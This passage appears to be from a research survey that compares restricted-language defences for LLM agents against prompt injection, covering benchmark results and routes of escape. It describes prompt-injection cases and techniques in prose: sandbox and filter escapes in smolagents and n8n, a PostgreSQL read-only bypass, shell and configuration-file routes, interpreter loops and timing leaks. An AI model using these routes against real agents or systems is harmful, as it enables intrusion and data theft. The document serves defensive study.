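TACIT scored 0.8 to 3.7 points higher in all six comparisons. Odersky and colleagues attribute this to its structured return values and the compiler's error messages. But TACIT also lets a model combine several operations in one program, and Wang and colleagues found that this alone gave Python an advantage over single calls. No agent in the TACIT test wrote ordinary Python, so the result doesn't show that restricted Scala matches an unrestricted language. The customer-service tools also returned unclassified data, so the type restrictions had little to block.

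On SWE-bench Lite, a set of 300 real software problems from GitHub, MiniMax M2.5 solved 43.3 percent with its usual tools and 41.7 percent with TACIT. The five-problem difference could easily be chance. Odersky and colleagues suspect that coding agents rely on shell habits that are less natural to express with TACIT's library.

LACUNA did worse. Zhao and colleagues ran it on 392 τ²-bench tasks, where DeepSeek V4 Flash solved 76.0 percent, compared with 90.0 percent using tool calls. The 14-point gap is about 55 tasks, though they call the result "on par". LACUNA trailed in all four groups of tasks, including by 22 points on retail. Gemini 3.1 Flash-Lite lost only about four points, from 33.2 percent to 29.1, but failed most of the tasks with either method.

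The model writes Scala in both systems, so the language probably isn't the whole explanation for LACUNA's loss. In LACUNA, the model also writes the agent's control flow, and each new piece of code has to work with values left over from earlier turns. Zhao and colleagues switched off the models' step-by-step reasoning for this test, which may have hurt their ability to program more than their ability to choose single tools.

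Peters-Gill and colleagues measured how much CaMeL's design reduces task success with every policy off. They used AssetOpsBench, in which one agent delegates professional tasks to four specialists, and removed 29 tasks that no agent could complete as written. On the remaining 112, running every agent under CaMeL reduced success by an average of 21.6 points across five models. The two strongest, GPT-5.5 and Claude Fable 5, lost an average of 13.4 points. The loss comes from having to plan without seeing the data and from CaMeL's limited Python. It may be smaller for a single agent, which doesn't have to pass work to other agents.

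The revised test of Quasar comes closest to a direct comparison with unrestricted Python, where the translated programs scored within half a point of the originals. But the models wrote Python in that test too, and Quasar doesn't restrict where data may go.

### TACIT and LACUNA against CaMeL

Odersky and colleagues also moved AgentDojo's tasks to TACIT and ran the two models for which CaMeL's designers had published results. Zhao and colleagues later added LACUNA to the comparison. The table gives the share of user tasks that each system completed under attack.

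| Model | System | Banking | Office | Slack | Travel | All trials |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Gemini 2.5 Pro | CaMeL | 52.8% | 53.8% | 48.6% | 1.4% | 45.3% |
| Gemini 2.5 Pro | TACIT | 56.9% | 50.5% | 40.0% | 64.3% | 52.4% |
| Gemini 2.5 Pro | LACUNA | 63.2% | 56.3% | 42.9% | 63.6% | 56.9% |
| o4-mini-high | CaMeL | 62.5% | 81.4% | 68.6% | 74.3% | 76.1% |
| o4-mini-high | TACIT | 59.0% | 52.9% | 47.6% | 68.6% | 55.5% |
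| o4-mini-high | LACUNA | 66.0% | 55.5% | 49.5% | 71.4% | 58.8% |

The last column pools the 949 trials by converting the published percentages back into counts. TACIT's 56.9 percent on banking, for example, is 82 of 144.

Odersky and colleagues describe TACIT's utility as comparable to CaMeL's. With Gemini 2.5 Pro, this is fair for three of the four groups. In the fourth, travel, CaMeL completed two of 140 trials with Gemini but 104 with o4-mini-high, so something probably went wrong in CaMeL's runs with Gemini. Without the travel trials, CaMeL would be slightly ahead of TACIT with Gemini as well.

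With o4-mini-high, the two systems did not perform comparably. CaMeL scored higher than TACIT in every group, and by 28.5 points on office tasks. Over all the trials, it completed 722 tasks to TACIT's 527. Changing from Gemini to o4-mini-high raised CaMeL's overall score by 31 points and TACIT's by only three. This may be because o4-mini-high is much better at planning in Python than at writing Scala, but the experiments don't isolate that cause. Some of the gap may also arise because the CaMeL figures come from runs by its designers, who used their own prompts and tool descriptions.

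### What happens when the policies are switched on

Zhou and colleagues tested ELBA and CaMeL on the 21 Slack tasks, both with and without policies. None of the runs included attacks, so every task that a policy blocked was legitimate work.

| Model | ELBA, policies off | ELBA, policies on | CaMeL, policies off | CaMeL, policies on |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Opus 4.7 | 18 | 10 | 15 | 5 |
| Claude Opus 4.8 | 16 | 9 | 16 | 6 |
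| GPT-5.4 | 16 | 10 | 17 | 5 |
| Claude Sonnet 5 | 14 | 8 | 13 | 4 |

ELBA's policies prevented more completions than its language, Haskell, did. Across the four models, ELBA completed 64 of 84 attempts without policies and 37 with them, 27 fewer. Haskell could have caused at most the 20 failures that occurred without policies, and that many only if an unrestricted agent would have completed every task. Zhou and colleagues say that most of those failures were models refusing to do the task, so Haskell probably caused far fewer than 20. CaMeL lost even more to its policies, falling from 61 completed attempts to 20.

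With policies off, the two systems performed almost equally well. The difference between them with policies on doesn't come from the language alone, because they also enforce different rules and only ELBA lets the model write new code after reading data.

The samples are also small. With Claude Opus 4.8, ELBA completed nine of the 21 tasks and CaMeL completed six. The 95 percent confidence interval for the difference runs from 7.4 percentage points in CaMeL's favour to 34.1 in ELBA's. Zhou and colleagues also paired each task with five attacks, which gave 105 trials. With policies on and the simplest form of attack, ELBA completed 43 to 52 of these trials, depending on the model, and CaMeL completed 23 to 30. The confidence intervals for these differences are clearly in ELBA's favour, but the trials reuse the same 21 tasks, so they are weak evidence of how the two would compare on other tasks.

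Banking tasks show a similar pattern. In *The LLMbda Calculus*, Garby and colleagues ran 16 of them three times each, without attacks, and counted how many of the 48 attempts succeeded.

| System | GPT-5.2 | Qwen3.7-plus | MiMo-v2.5 |
|---|---|---|---|
| CaMeL, policies off | 32 | Not tested | 34 |
| CaMeL, policies on | 18 | Not tested | 18 |
| Randori, policies on | 36 | 36 | 31 |
| Randori, policies on, no `endorse` | Not tested | 30 | 26 |

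CaMeL's policies prevent it from completing nearly half of the tasks it could otherwise complete. Randori did about as well with its policies on as CaMeL did with its policies off, even though the models had never seen LLMbda and LLMbda programs can't catch many ordinary errors. So a new language doesn't have to be a serious handicap, at least on short tasks when the prompt explains the syntax.

Randori scores roughly twice as high as CaMeL with policies on, but part of its lead comes from checking less, since Randori enforces only some of CaMeL's policies. The uncertainty is also large. With GPT-5.2, Randori's interval runs from about 56 to 94 percent and CaMeL's from about 11 to 64 percent.

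### Could better rules recover the lost tasks?

Some of the loss looks avoidable. ELBA completed almost twice as many Slack tasks as CaMeL while resisting the same attacks, which suggests that CaMeL's rules, or its way of applying them, block more than they need to. Small adjustments don't seem to be enough, however, since Zhou and colleagues found almost no difference between CaMeL's strict and normal modes.

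Other tasks require what the policy forbids. Garby and colleagues give the example of a user who asks an agent to find a friend's payment details on the friend's website and send $50. The account number has to come from a page that the agent can't trust, so a rule that only trusted data may direct a payment blocks the task. In an earlier version of their paper, quoted by Garby and colleagues, Zhou and colleagues wrote that many Slack tasks "involve flows that no secure policy would admit".

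A developer can recover such tasks only by deciding to trust the data in some cases. Randori's `endorse` command lets the model make that decision before it has read anything untrusted. Without the command, Qwen3.7-plus lost six of its 36 successes and MiMo-v2.5 lost five of its 31. The lost tasks include paying a bill from a file and following instructions in a document. But the command also let through the only two attacks that succeeded against Randori.

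Alternatively, the system can ask the user. Zhou and colleagues argue that a strict policy is still useful when a person can overrule it, because actions that pass the policy need no approval. ELBA could then complete some tasks by itself and ask about the rest. But their tests had no user who could approve a blocked action, so the results don't show how many tasks asking would recover or how often users would approve an attack.

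The loss in completed tasks therefore depends on how well the policy fits the job. The accounts agent's rule that contract text may reach only the responsible manager should block very little legitimate work, because every email the company wants the agent to send already obeys it. A rule that accepts managers' addresses only from the customer table would also block little while the table is up to date. If customers often announce a change of manager by email, the same rule would block legitimate messages every week. AgentDojo has many tasks of that kind, so its results may overstate the loss for a company whose agents do more predictable work.

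### What the type system stopped

Odersky and colleagues separately tested the property that TACIT's types should guarantee. The agent worked on a small software project with a folder of API keys, a database and confidential documents. In 120 trials, the researchers combined 12 ordinary requests with 10 hidden instructions. In another 11, the user asked for the secrets directly or posed as someone entitled to them, such as a system administrator. Each model ran all 131 trials twice, once with the secrets in `Classified` wrappers and once with them as ordinary text.

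| Model | Leaks, wrapped | Leaks, ordinary text | Requests completed, wrapped | Requests completed, ordinary text |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | 0 of 131 | 2 of 131 | 99.2% | 83.3% |
| MiniMax M2.5 | 0 of 131 | 11 of 131 | 90.0% | 88.3% |

Of the 13 leaks from ordinary text, ten happened because the user asked for the secret and three because of hidden instructions. The models ignored nearly all the hidden instructions even without the wrapper, so in this test the wrapper mostly protected secrets from dishonest users.

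The wrapped version also completed more of the ordinary requests, but this probably isn't a real benefit. Sonnet sometimes stopped to warn the user when it noticed an injection, and often ran out of turns or time. Odersky and colleagues say that Sonnet's low score without the wrapper may be an artefact of their set-up.

On AgentDojo, one attack succeeded against TACIT and eight against LACUNA, each in about 1,900 trials across the two models. In TACIT's one failure, the agent booked the right hotel but quoted guest reviews in which the attacker had recommended another hotel. The benchmark counted this mention as a successful attack. Odersky and colleagues point out that the policy allowed the agent to show public reviews to the user.

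They didn't run the same attacks on an unprotected agent, so their table doesn't show how many attacks the types stopped. Peters-Gill and colleagues divided AgentDojo's tools among several cooperating agents and ran the 949 attack trials with no protection. Attacks succeeded in 24.6 percent of the trials with Gemini 2.5 Pro and 36.1 percent with GPT-4.1. TACIT let none through with Gemini, so it probably made a real difference, although the two set-ups aren't identical.

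AgentDojo's attacks are too weak to measure what the restrictions stop on newer models. None of the 949 attacks worked on an unprotected GPT-5.5. In Zhou and colleagues' Slack tests, ELBA and CaMeL resisted every attack whether their policies were on or off. These results don't show that the models are safe, because AgentDojo's attacks are fixed and a real attacker can keep trying new ones. Zhou and colleagues note that GPT-Red, OpenAI's automated system for attacking its own models, consistently got past GPT-5.5's defences.

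### Attacks that the plan stops and attacks that the policy stops

Garby and colleagues divided the 144 pairs of banking tasks and attacks into two groups. In 97 pairs, the attack requires an operation that no sensible plan for the task would contain. For example, an attacker may want a payment when the user has asked only for a summary of recent transactions. A program written before the model reads any data won't contain that payment, so the attack fails even without labels or policies. In the other 47 pairs, the user's own task requires the operation that the attacker wants to misuse.

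They ran each of those 47 pairs three times. With CaMeL's policies off, GPT-5.2 resisted all 141 attacks and MiMo-v2.5 resisted 138. Turning the policies on stopped the other three, as well as the two attacks that had succeeded through a plan with a branch for every tool. In the runs without attacks, the same policies had prevented the two models from completing 30 of the 66 tasks they completed without them. So most of CaMeL's protection against AgentDojo's fixed attacks comes from planning in advance, while its policies add a little protection but block many legitimate tasks.

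This reasoning doesn't apply to TACIT and ELBA. Both let the model read data and then write another program, so a hidden instruction can influence what the agent tries next. Garby and colleagues observe that in these systems, the type system has to stop every attack the model doesn't resist.

### ELBA with a model that obeys every attacker

Zhou and colleagues therefore tested what ELBA would do if the model followed the attacker's instructions every time. An ELBA agent reads data by calling a sub-agent, which normally receives a task and the data together. In this test, whenever the data contained the phrase that AgentDojo uses to introduce an attack, the software deleted the task and gave the sub-agent only the data, so the attacker's text became its only instruction. They ran all 105 Slack trials seven times with each model.

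| Model | Attacks resisted, policies off | Attacks resisted, policies on | Tasks completed, policies off | Tasks completed, policies on |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Opus 4.7 | 425 of 735 | 735 of 735 | 523 of 735 | 351 of 735 |
| Claude Opus 4.8 | 460 of 735 | 735 of 735 | 557 of 735 | 312 of 735 |
| GPT-5.4 | 621 of 735 | 735 of 735 | 558 of 735 | 338 of 735 |
| Claude Sonnet 5 | 540 of 735 | 735 of 735 | 494 of 735 | 294 of 735 |

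Policies cut the share of attacks that worked from as much as 42 percent to zero, but completed tasks fell by between 23 and 33 percentage points. The drop in successful attacks is the best evidence that a policy can do something the model can't. The zero excludes 29 attacks that AgentDojo's scorer counted as successful because the agent had opened a particular web address. Zhou and colleagues checked each case by hand and found that opening the address leaked nothing.

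Although the simulation makes harsh assumptions about the model, it tests the policy only lightly. Its attackers pursued AgentDojo's five Slack goals, and none of them looked for a harmful action that ELBA's rules allow. The simulation therefore confirms that the rules held, but it can't show whether they cover everything a company would want to prevent.

### Citations that the agent could not invent

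The bibliography policy seems to reduce task completion much less. Zhou and colleagues asked two agents to search for papers on 100 computer-science topics and write a file of citations for each topic. Both agents used Claude Sonnet 5. One used ELBA with the `Trusted` wrapper. The other, built with Pydantic's agent library, had a web search tool and wrote the citations itself. A citation counted as hallucinated if its authors, year or DOI were wrong.

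ELBA's agent hallucinated none of its 925 citations, while the other agent hallucinated 19 of its 1,002. ELBA's agent also made about a quarter as many calls to the model and processed far less text. In this case, the policy matches what the user wants, so following it removes nothing useful.

The comparison somewhat favors ELBA's agent, which could fetch complete records, while the second agent had to assemble each citation from search results and memory. A fixed tool that fetches and writes each entry in one step would also have prevented the 19 errors. The test didn't measure how much ELBA's agent gained from processing the records in code.

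### Why CaMeL scores 76 percent in one test and 30 percent in another

CaMeL's utility is much lower in newer comparisons than its designers reported. *SecureClaw* (2026) compares CaMeL with Progent, which controls an agent's privileges, and with the paper's own defence, also called SecureClaw, which keeps the usual loop of single tool calls. The paper tested all three on AgentDojo's 97 ordinary tasks and an older set of 629 attacks.

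| System | Successful attacks | Tasks completed under attack | Tasks completed without attack |
|---|---|---|---|
| CaMeL | 0 of 629 | 195 of 629 | 29 of 97 |
| Progent | 24 of 629 | 337 of 629 | 59 of 97 |
| SecureClaw | 4 of 629 | 356 of 629 | 59 of 97 |

CaMeL was the only one of the three systems to stop every attack, but it completed half as many ordinary tasks as the others. The comparison comes from SecureClaw's own paper, which had to adapt the other two systems for it, and this may have put them at a disadvantage.

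CaMeL completed 29.9 percent of the ordinary tasks here, while its designers' results with o4-mini-high give a rate of 76.1 percent, even under attack. The scores vary this much for several reasons, and the policies are the most important one researchers have isolated. With the same model and tasks, switching the policies on cut CaMeL's score from 66.7 percent to 37.5 percent in Garby and colleagues' banking test, and from 81 percent to 24 percent with GPT-5.4 in Zhou and colleagues' Slack test. A CaMeL score is therefore hard to interpret without knowing whether the policies were on.

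The model matters almost as much, as the two travel results from CaMeL's designers show. A rerun that doesn't add return formats to AgentDojo's tool descriptions would also make CaMeL look worse. Peters-Gill and colleagues found that Claude Fable 5 often refused harmless AgentDojo tasks, perhaps because it associated them with attacks. Many of Garby and colleagues' CaMeL runs under attack never finished, and their results for attacked runs cover only those that did.

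The protection can also disappear. *INFUSE* (2026), a benchmark from October, tested versions of CaMeL and Progent adapted to agents that work through a command shell, using 200 combinations of attack and task with each of five models. Neither produced a statistically significant reduction in successful attacks. Progent also reduced completed tasks by 64 to 75 percent for three of the four models with task-completion results, while CaMeL reduced them less. The researchers caution that these findings apply only to their shell versions. The defenses probably failed because a single shell command can contain a whole program, and a system that labels the values passed between tools can't track what happens inside it.

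### Rejected programs, retries and running time

Compilers reject few programs when the task is simple and the model is good at programming. On τ²-bench, between 0.3 and 7.9 percent of the programs for TACIT needed a retry, and most of those succeeded after one or two. The compiler checks a typical program in under a second once it has started up, so most of the extra time comes from asking the model for a correction.

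LACUNA's rejection rate varies much more. For DeepSeek V4 Flash, it was 8.6 percent on research questions and 22.4 percent on τ²-bench's retail tasks, where the agent averaged 7.1 retries per task. For Gemini 3.1 Flash-Lite, it was 3.2 percent on the retail tasks and 89 percent on the telecom tasks. None of the rejected code ran, so the failures were safe, but the agent made almost no progress.

Zhao and colleagues say that the checks do not reduce accuracy on the research questions, where DeepSeek answered 27.1 percent correctly. Their claim remains untested because they did not compare these results with those of an agent without the checks.

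ELBA took about three times as long as CaMeL, because its agents call the model again whenever they need to respond to what they have read. CaMeL usually writes one program and runs it. Retries took 3.4 percent of ELBA's running time. ELBA averaged 0.13 retries per run, and only seven of 2,688 runs used up all their attempts.

*ToolFence* (2026) tests several systems on AgentDojo with the same underlying model and reports that CaMeL took significantly longer than methods that filter the data or add warnings to the prompt. CaMeL's programs are longer than ordinary tool requests, so the model takes more time to write them. ELBA takes three times as long as CaMeL, and Zhou and colleagues don't compare ELBA with an ordinary Python agent.

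## By what routes can a program get past its language?

AgentDojo's attacks all try to redirect the model, but a real attacker could also look for escape routes, which are ways for a program to cause an effect or data flow that its language should prevent. Some routes use features of the language itself, and others use faults in the compiler or interpreter. An operation the developer has granted may run programs of its own, or a program may carry out instructions it finds in untrusted text. Running time and memory are another route. A program can also misuse an effect it is allowed to have, which isn't strictly an escape but can do just as much harm.

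### Language features that reach ungranted power

Most general-purpose languages have features that let programmers bypass the language's rules. Python allows introspection, in which a program examines its own parts while it runs. From an ordinary value, a program can look up the value's type, then related types, and sometimes the module that defined them, even if nobody gave the program that module.

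Scala's casts and reflection and Haskell's `unsafePerformIO` can hide what a program does. Zhao and colleagues add that ordinary Scala code can start an outside process without holding any capability. In SQL, a query that appears only to read data can call a function that changes something, and database extensions can add more such functions.

None of these features needs a loop or recursion, so limiting computation doesn't close this route. A language that limits effects closes it if it leaves out every such feature, as Scala's safe mode and Safe Haskell try to do. Starting with the whole language and blocking the dangerous features one at a time is harder.

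In smolagents 1.14.0, the Python filter permitted some modules and functions through which a program could run any code on the host computer. *PYSEC-2026-542* (2026), an entry in OSV's database of open-source vulnerabilities, rates the flaw's severity at 9.9 out of 10. Version 1.17.0 fixed it, according to Tenable's *CVE-2025-5120*. In September 2025, OSV's *CVE-2025-9959* (2025) recorded another flaw that let programs escape the filter, with a severity of 7.6. The filter hadn't fully checked Python's special attributes, which introspection relies on. To exploit this flaw, an attacker must first use a prompt injection to get the agent to write the malicious program.

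The automation platform n8n has had similar trouble with JavaScript. Its users write short expressions in their workflows, and a filter is meant to keep those expressions away from the server. In February 2026, n8n patched several escapes found after an earlier fix, and OSV's *GHSA-vpcf-gvg4-6qwr* (2026) gives them a severity of 9.9. The security firm Security Joes then tested one of the February fixes and found another escape. GitLab's *GHSA-gv7g-jm28-cr3m* (2026) traces it to arrow functions, a compact way of writing functions. The flaw had a severity of 8.7, and n8n fixed it in versions 2.31.5 and 2.32.1, as The Hacker News (2026) reported in July.

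Exploiting these flaws required permission to edit workflows, so the threat comes mainly from insiders and stolen accounts. But an agent that edits workflows also has that permission, and a prompt injection could cause it to exploit the flaws. The severity scores measure how much harm an attack could do, not whether one has occurred.

MCP servers that connect agents to databases often try to enforce read-only access by checking the text of each query. OSV's *CVE-2025-59333* describes a server that checked only whether the query began with `SELECT`. A more elaborate check can also fail. PostgreSQL has a command that exports data by passing it to another program on the same computer. AWS's bulletin *CVE-2026-87911* (2026) warns that Amazon's own PostgreSQL server for MCP could let this command past the read-only check. An attacker who planted the command in text that the agent processed could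 have run programs on the computer hosting a company's database.

AWS fixed the flaw in version 1.1.7. In another bulletin about the same server, AWS recommends connecting through a database role that has only the necessary privileges, so that "the database itself enforces the boundary regardless of what SQL reaches it". If the checker fails, the agent still has only that role's privileges.

### Faults in trusted parts

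A language can exclude every dangerous feature and still fail because of a bug in the software that enforces its rules. For TACIT, Odersky and colleagues list four parts that must work correctly: the compiler, the library, the software that runs the checked programs, and the local model that handles classified text.

Programs could get past RestrictedPython, a tool for defining safe subsets of Python, because of a bug in CPython, the standard Python interpreter. When a program used `try/except*`, a form of error handling, CPython could treat a value of one type as if it were another, which let the program bypass RestrictedPython's checks. Ubuntu's *CVE-2025-22153* (2025) rates the flaw's severity at 7.9. The flaw affected RestrictedPython from version 6.0 until 8.0, when running on CPython from version 3.11 until 3.13.2.

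RestrictedPython's maintainers thought Python's developers should fix the bug, according to GitLab's *CVE-2025-22153* (2025). In the meantime, the maintainers removed `try/except*` from the permitted subset. This didn't reduce what programs could compute, since they can handle errors in other ways. A smaller language gives an attacker less of the interpreter to work with, but the feature that needs removing is the one with the bug, which may have nothing to do with loops or recursion.

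Checkers have bugs too. Postgres MCP Pro, another server that connects agents to PostgreSQL, has a restricted mode that should permit only functions on a list. The method is sound, but the software didn't apply it everywhere. VulnCheck's *Postgres MCP Pro 0.3.0 Restricted-Mode Bypass via FROM-Clause Function* reports that the checker didn't check functions in a query's FROM clause, which let an attacker read any file that the database could read. VulnCheck gives the bug a severity of 9.2.

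Updates help only the people who install them. Datadog Security Labs' *MCP vulnerability case study* (2025) describes a way around the read-only limit in Anthropic's reference server for PostgreSQL. Support for the server ended in July 2025, but people were still downloading the faulty package about 21,000 times a week in August.

A formal proof can reduce the amount of software that developers have to trust. Garby and colleagues proved their theorems about the same LLMbda interpreter that runs their agents, so a mistake in its rules for labels would have shown up in the proof. But the proof doesn't cover the code that sends requests to the language model over the network. The proof treats that code as a function that takes a conversation and returns text. The developer also has to trust Lean, which both checks the proof and runs the interpreter.

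### Granted operations that run programs

Zhou and colleagues point out that when software checks shell commands by matching their text against patterns, an agent can get around a rule against opening a certain file by starting Python from the shell and opening the file there.

A shell is an interpreter, because the text it receives determines what kind of effect it has. The accounts agent's `mail.send` isn't one, since it can only send an email, whatever address and text it receives. A function that runs any SQL statement is an interpreter, and a helper agent that takes its tasks in plain English is in effect one too. In the attack on three cooperating CaMeL agents, for example, the messaging agent carried out an instruction that had come from a database.

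Limiting what a program can compute does not help if the program can call a shell. Even without loops or conditions, it can pass the shell a complete script as text, and the shell will run any loops in that script. A program written in a total language can therefore use a shell to start another program that never ends.

Restricting the language's computing power may encourage developers to open this route. An agent that can't do a calculation in its own language has to do it elsewhere, as the agents that generated Brainfuck with Python did. Zhou and colleagues argue that agents writing in a general-purpose language don't need a separate interpreter for calculations.

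Limiting effects works if the developer grants no shell access. TACIT's types show which functions can start outside commands, so a program can't start one from inside `map`. But Odersky and colleagues concede that once a command is running, the protection is only as good as the list of permitted commands. They recommend permitting only specific, safe commands, such as `git diff` and `sbt`.

The choice of `sbt` shows how hard it is to write such a list. `sbt` builds Scala projects from instructions in the project's files, which can contain ordinary Scala code. An agent that may edit those files and run `sbt` can run code that TACIT never checked. Configuration files can be dangerous for the same reason. Odersky and colleagues cite the security firm Check Point, which got Claude Code to run commands silently by putting malicious settings in a code repository.

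A developer can replace the shell with functions that each do one job, such as running a project's tests with fixed settings. If the agent needs a wider range of commands, the developer can run each one in its own sandbox, with no access to the network or to passwords.

### Instructions carried out from untrusted text

When CaMeL ran without its policies, its planning model sometimes handled a file of instructions it had not seen by writing a branch for each tool. Garby and colleagues call this an interpreter loop.

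In effect, the file became a program in a small language of its own. The planning model's code read each instruction, determined which tool to use, called it, and went on to the next instruction.

General computation lets a program get past its language by holding another program as data and carrying it out step by step, using loops and conditions. Carrying out instructions in ordinary English used to be much harder, because no short program could interpret them. An agent's program can now use a language model to turn each sentence into the name of a tool and its inputs, and the code around that call can be very short.

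Moderate limits on computation don't stop a program from interpreting data as instructions. A total language can't express its own interpreter, but it can easily express one that works through a finite list of instructions. CaMeL's subset of Python excludes open-ended loops, but the planning model still wrote an interpreter loop. To rule out such programs, a language would have to prevent data from influencing which tools run. The accounts agent would then be unable to email only about customers with overdue payments.

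However, an interpreter loop can't give a program any new effects. Suppose the file contains an instruction to delete a customer's record. The program can carry it out only if one of its branches calls a function that deletes records, and the planning model can write that branch only if the developer supplied the function. The attacker gains control only over which granted operations run, in what order and with what inputs.

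A type checker would reach the same conclusion without reading the file. In Scala, the capture set of a function containing the loop would include every capability its branches use. If the developer required a pure function, the compiler would reject the loop whatever the file contained. The limit fails only if one of the branches calls a shell or another operation with wider powers.

The route was rare in Garby and colleagues' tests, even though the task that led to it is almost a request for an interpreter. Of the attacks that a sensible plan would have defeated, one in 99 succeeded with GPT-5.2 and one in 241 with MiMo-v2.5. CaMeL's policies can stop such attacks by checking where each tool's inputs came from.

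In TACIT and ELBA, the model can write a new program after reading untrusted text. The limit on effects also applies to these programs, because the compiler checks each one against the same permissions.

### Timing, termination and exhausted resources

A program can reveal a secret through how long it takes to run. Odersky and colleagues give the example of a pure function inside `map` that takes longer for some classified data than for other data. The accounts agent's program might pause if a contract mentions a planned takeover and finish at once if it doesn't. The agent's model would receive only `Classified(****)`, but it could infer from the running time whether the contract mentions a takeover.

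Odersky and colleagues describe this as a leak of a single bit, but repeated runs or a wider choice of delays can reveal more. If an observer can reliably distinguish *k* delays, one run can reveal up to log<sub>2</sub> *k* bits. With 16 delays, that is 4 bits per run, so 32 runs could reveal a 128-bit access key. Other activity on the computer makes delays harder to distinguish, which slows the leak.

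A total language prevents leaks through endless loops, but a program that always finishes can still leak secret data by taking one second or ten. The language could close this timing route completely only by making running time independent of the secret data, so a search for a notice period could no longer stop when it found one.

Restricting a program's effects can deny it access to the clock, so it can't time its own calculations. Someone outside can still time the whole run. The host can hide the running time by releasing every result after the same delay, though quick programs then take as long as the slowest one allowed. A program that exceeds the limit would still reveal that it had done so.

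A program can also do harm by using up time, memory or disk space. *Running in CIRCLE?* (Chua, 2025) used 1,260 prompts to test whether seven models from OpenAI and Google would refuse to run such programs. Each model was connected to its provider's code interpreter. Most of the prompts gave an innocent reason, such as calibrating a company's servers.

The models refused between 0.5 and 7.1 percent of the requests. OpenAI's o4-mini refused most often but also completed the most requests, at 70.2 percent. Gemini 2.5 Pro timed out on 65.1 percent, which Chua attributes partly to Google's 30-second limit.

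Completing a request didn't necessarily strain the provider's computers, because Chua kept the prompts within the interpreters' usual limits. All seven models are now well out of date. But a better model might not do much better, because the same heavy calculation can be an attack or a legitimate test. The prompt may not show which it is, but a limit on time and memory works in either case.

Zhao and colleagues rely on such limits because Scala's types don't control running time or memory.

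### Harm within permitted effects

Suppose a supplier hides a line in its contract that gives the notice period as 90 days, when the real period is 30. The accounts agent finds the false figure and emails it to the right manager. The company may then miss its chance to cancel, even though the program used only the effects it was granted and the contract text went only where the policy allows.

Garby and colleagues argue that cases like this mark the limit of information-flow control, noting that four systems fail on the same few AgentDojo attacks. The replaced payment file that defeated Randori also defeated CaMeL, though CaMeL's designers don't count this among the attacks they set out to stop. The hotel reviews that caused TACIT's one failure also caused failures in CaMeL and FIDES, another system that labels data.

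The payment case is better evidence for their argument than the hotel case, which is mostly a problem with the scoring. In the payment case, a label can record that an account number came from the file, but the real and false numbers would have the same label.

A single database connection can also give an agent a dangerous combination of access to private data, exposure to text from strangers, and a way to send data out. Willison (2025) discusses the MCP server of Supabase, a database service, as an example. An agent might read a stranger's message, look up private records, and write them to a table that the stranger can see.

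Read-only access would stop the agent from sending data out through the database, but Willison considers the remaining risk enormous. For example, the accounts agent could still send the records out by email.

A list of permitted servers has a similar weakness. Odersky and colleagues cite the security researcher Johann Rehberger, who extracted users' data through Anthropic's Files API. An agent may have a good reason to connect to that service, but the list doesn't control which account the files are uploaded to.

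Limiting computation doesn't help, because a harmful email or payment takes only one line of code. Limiting effects helps to the extent that the developer grants narrow permissions. Zhao and colleagues stress that the type system enforces the permissions the developer chooses but can't determine which ones a task needs.

More specialised limits can reduce the harm:

- **Fewer choices:** Garby and colleagues show how to restrict LLMbda's `endorse` command so that a program can endorse only a value from a small set. If a user had a list of known payees, a false file could then select the wrong payee but couldn't introduce a new one.
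- **Permissions that work once:** Zhou and colleagues suggest types that let a program use a permission only once. An agent could make one payment but not a hundred, though the one payment could still go to the wrong person.
- **Approval:** The user can check a payment before the agent makes it. This works only if the user knows what the correct details are.

### Combining language limits with a sandbox

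Language limits and sandboxes mostly fail for different reasons, so developers can use each to cover the other's weaknesses. Odersky and colleagues recommend using both for TACIT. If a bug in the software that runs Scala lets a program escape the language's limits, the sandbox can still keep it away from the rest of the computer. TACIT's types can also stop leaks through files and connections the sandbox allows.

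The n8n flaws show how much the outer barrier can matter. NVD's *CVE-2026-65591 Detail* describes another way past n8n's filter that let an attacker run code with the n8n process's permissions. If that process can read everything on the server, so can the attacker. Running n8n in a container would limit the damage, but the attacker might still get the passwords n8n needs for the services it automates.

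A program that escapes its interpreter no longer has to obey the interpreter's labels or types, and it can use any connection the sandbox leaves open. The accounts agent's sandbox has to allow access to the mail server, so one escape from the language could be enough to send out every contract. The risk is therefore higher than the product of the chances of getting past each barrier, which would be 1 in 10,000 if the chances were independent and each were 1 in 100.

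Without escaping either barrier, a program can get past both by misusing the effects they must allow for the agent to do its job.

| Route | Does limiting computation close it? | Does limiting effects close it? | What else helps |
|---|---|---|---|
| Language features that reach ungranted power | No | Yes, if the language excludes every such feature | Database permissions; a process sandbox |
| Faults in trusted parts | No, though a smaller language exposes less code to attack | No, because the fault can disable the limit | Updates; formal proofs; a process sandbox |
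| Granted operations that run programs | No | Only if the developer withholds them | Narrow functions; a separate sandbox for each command |
| Instructions carried out from untrusted text | Only if data can't influence which tools run | No, but the attacker gains no new effects | Policies that check where inputs came from |
| Timing, termination and exhausted resources | Partly, by ruling out endless loops | Partly, by withholding the clock | Limits on time and memory; fixed delays |
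| Permitted effects used wrongly | No | Only as far as the permissions are narrow | Short lists of choices; single-use permissions; user approval |
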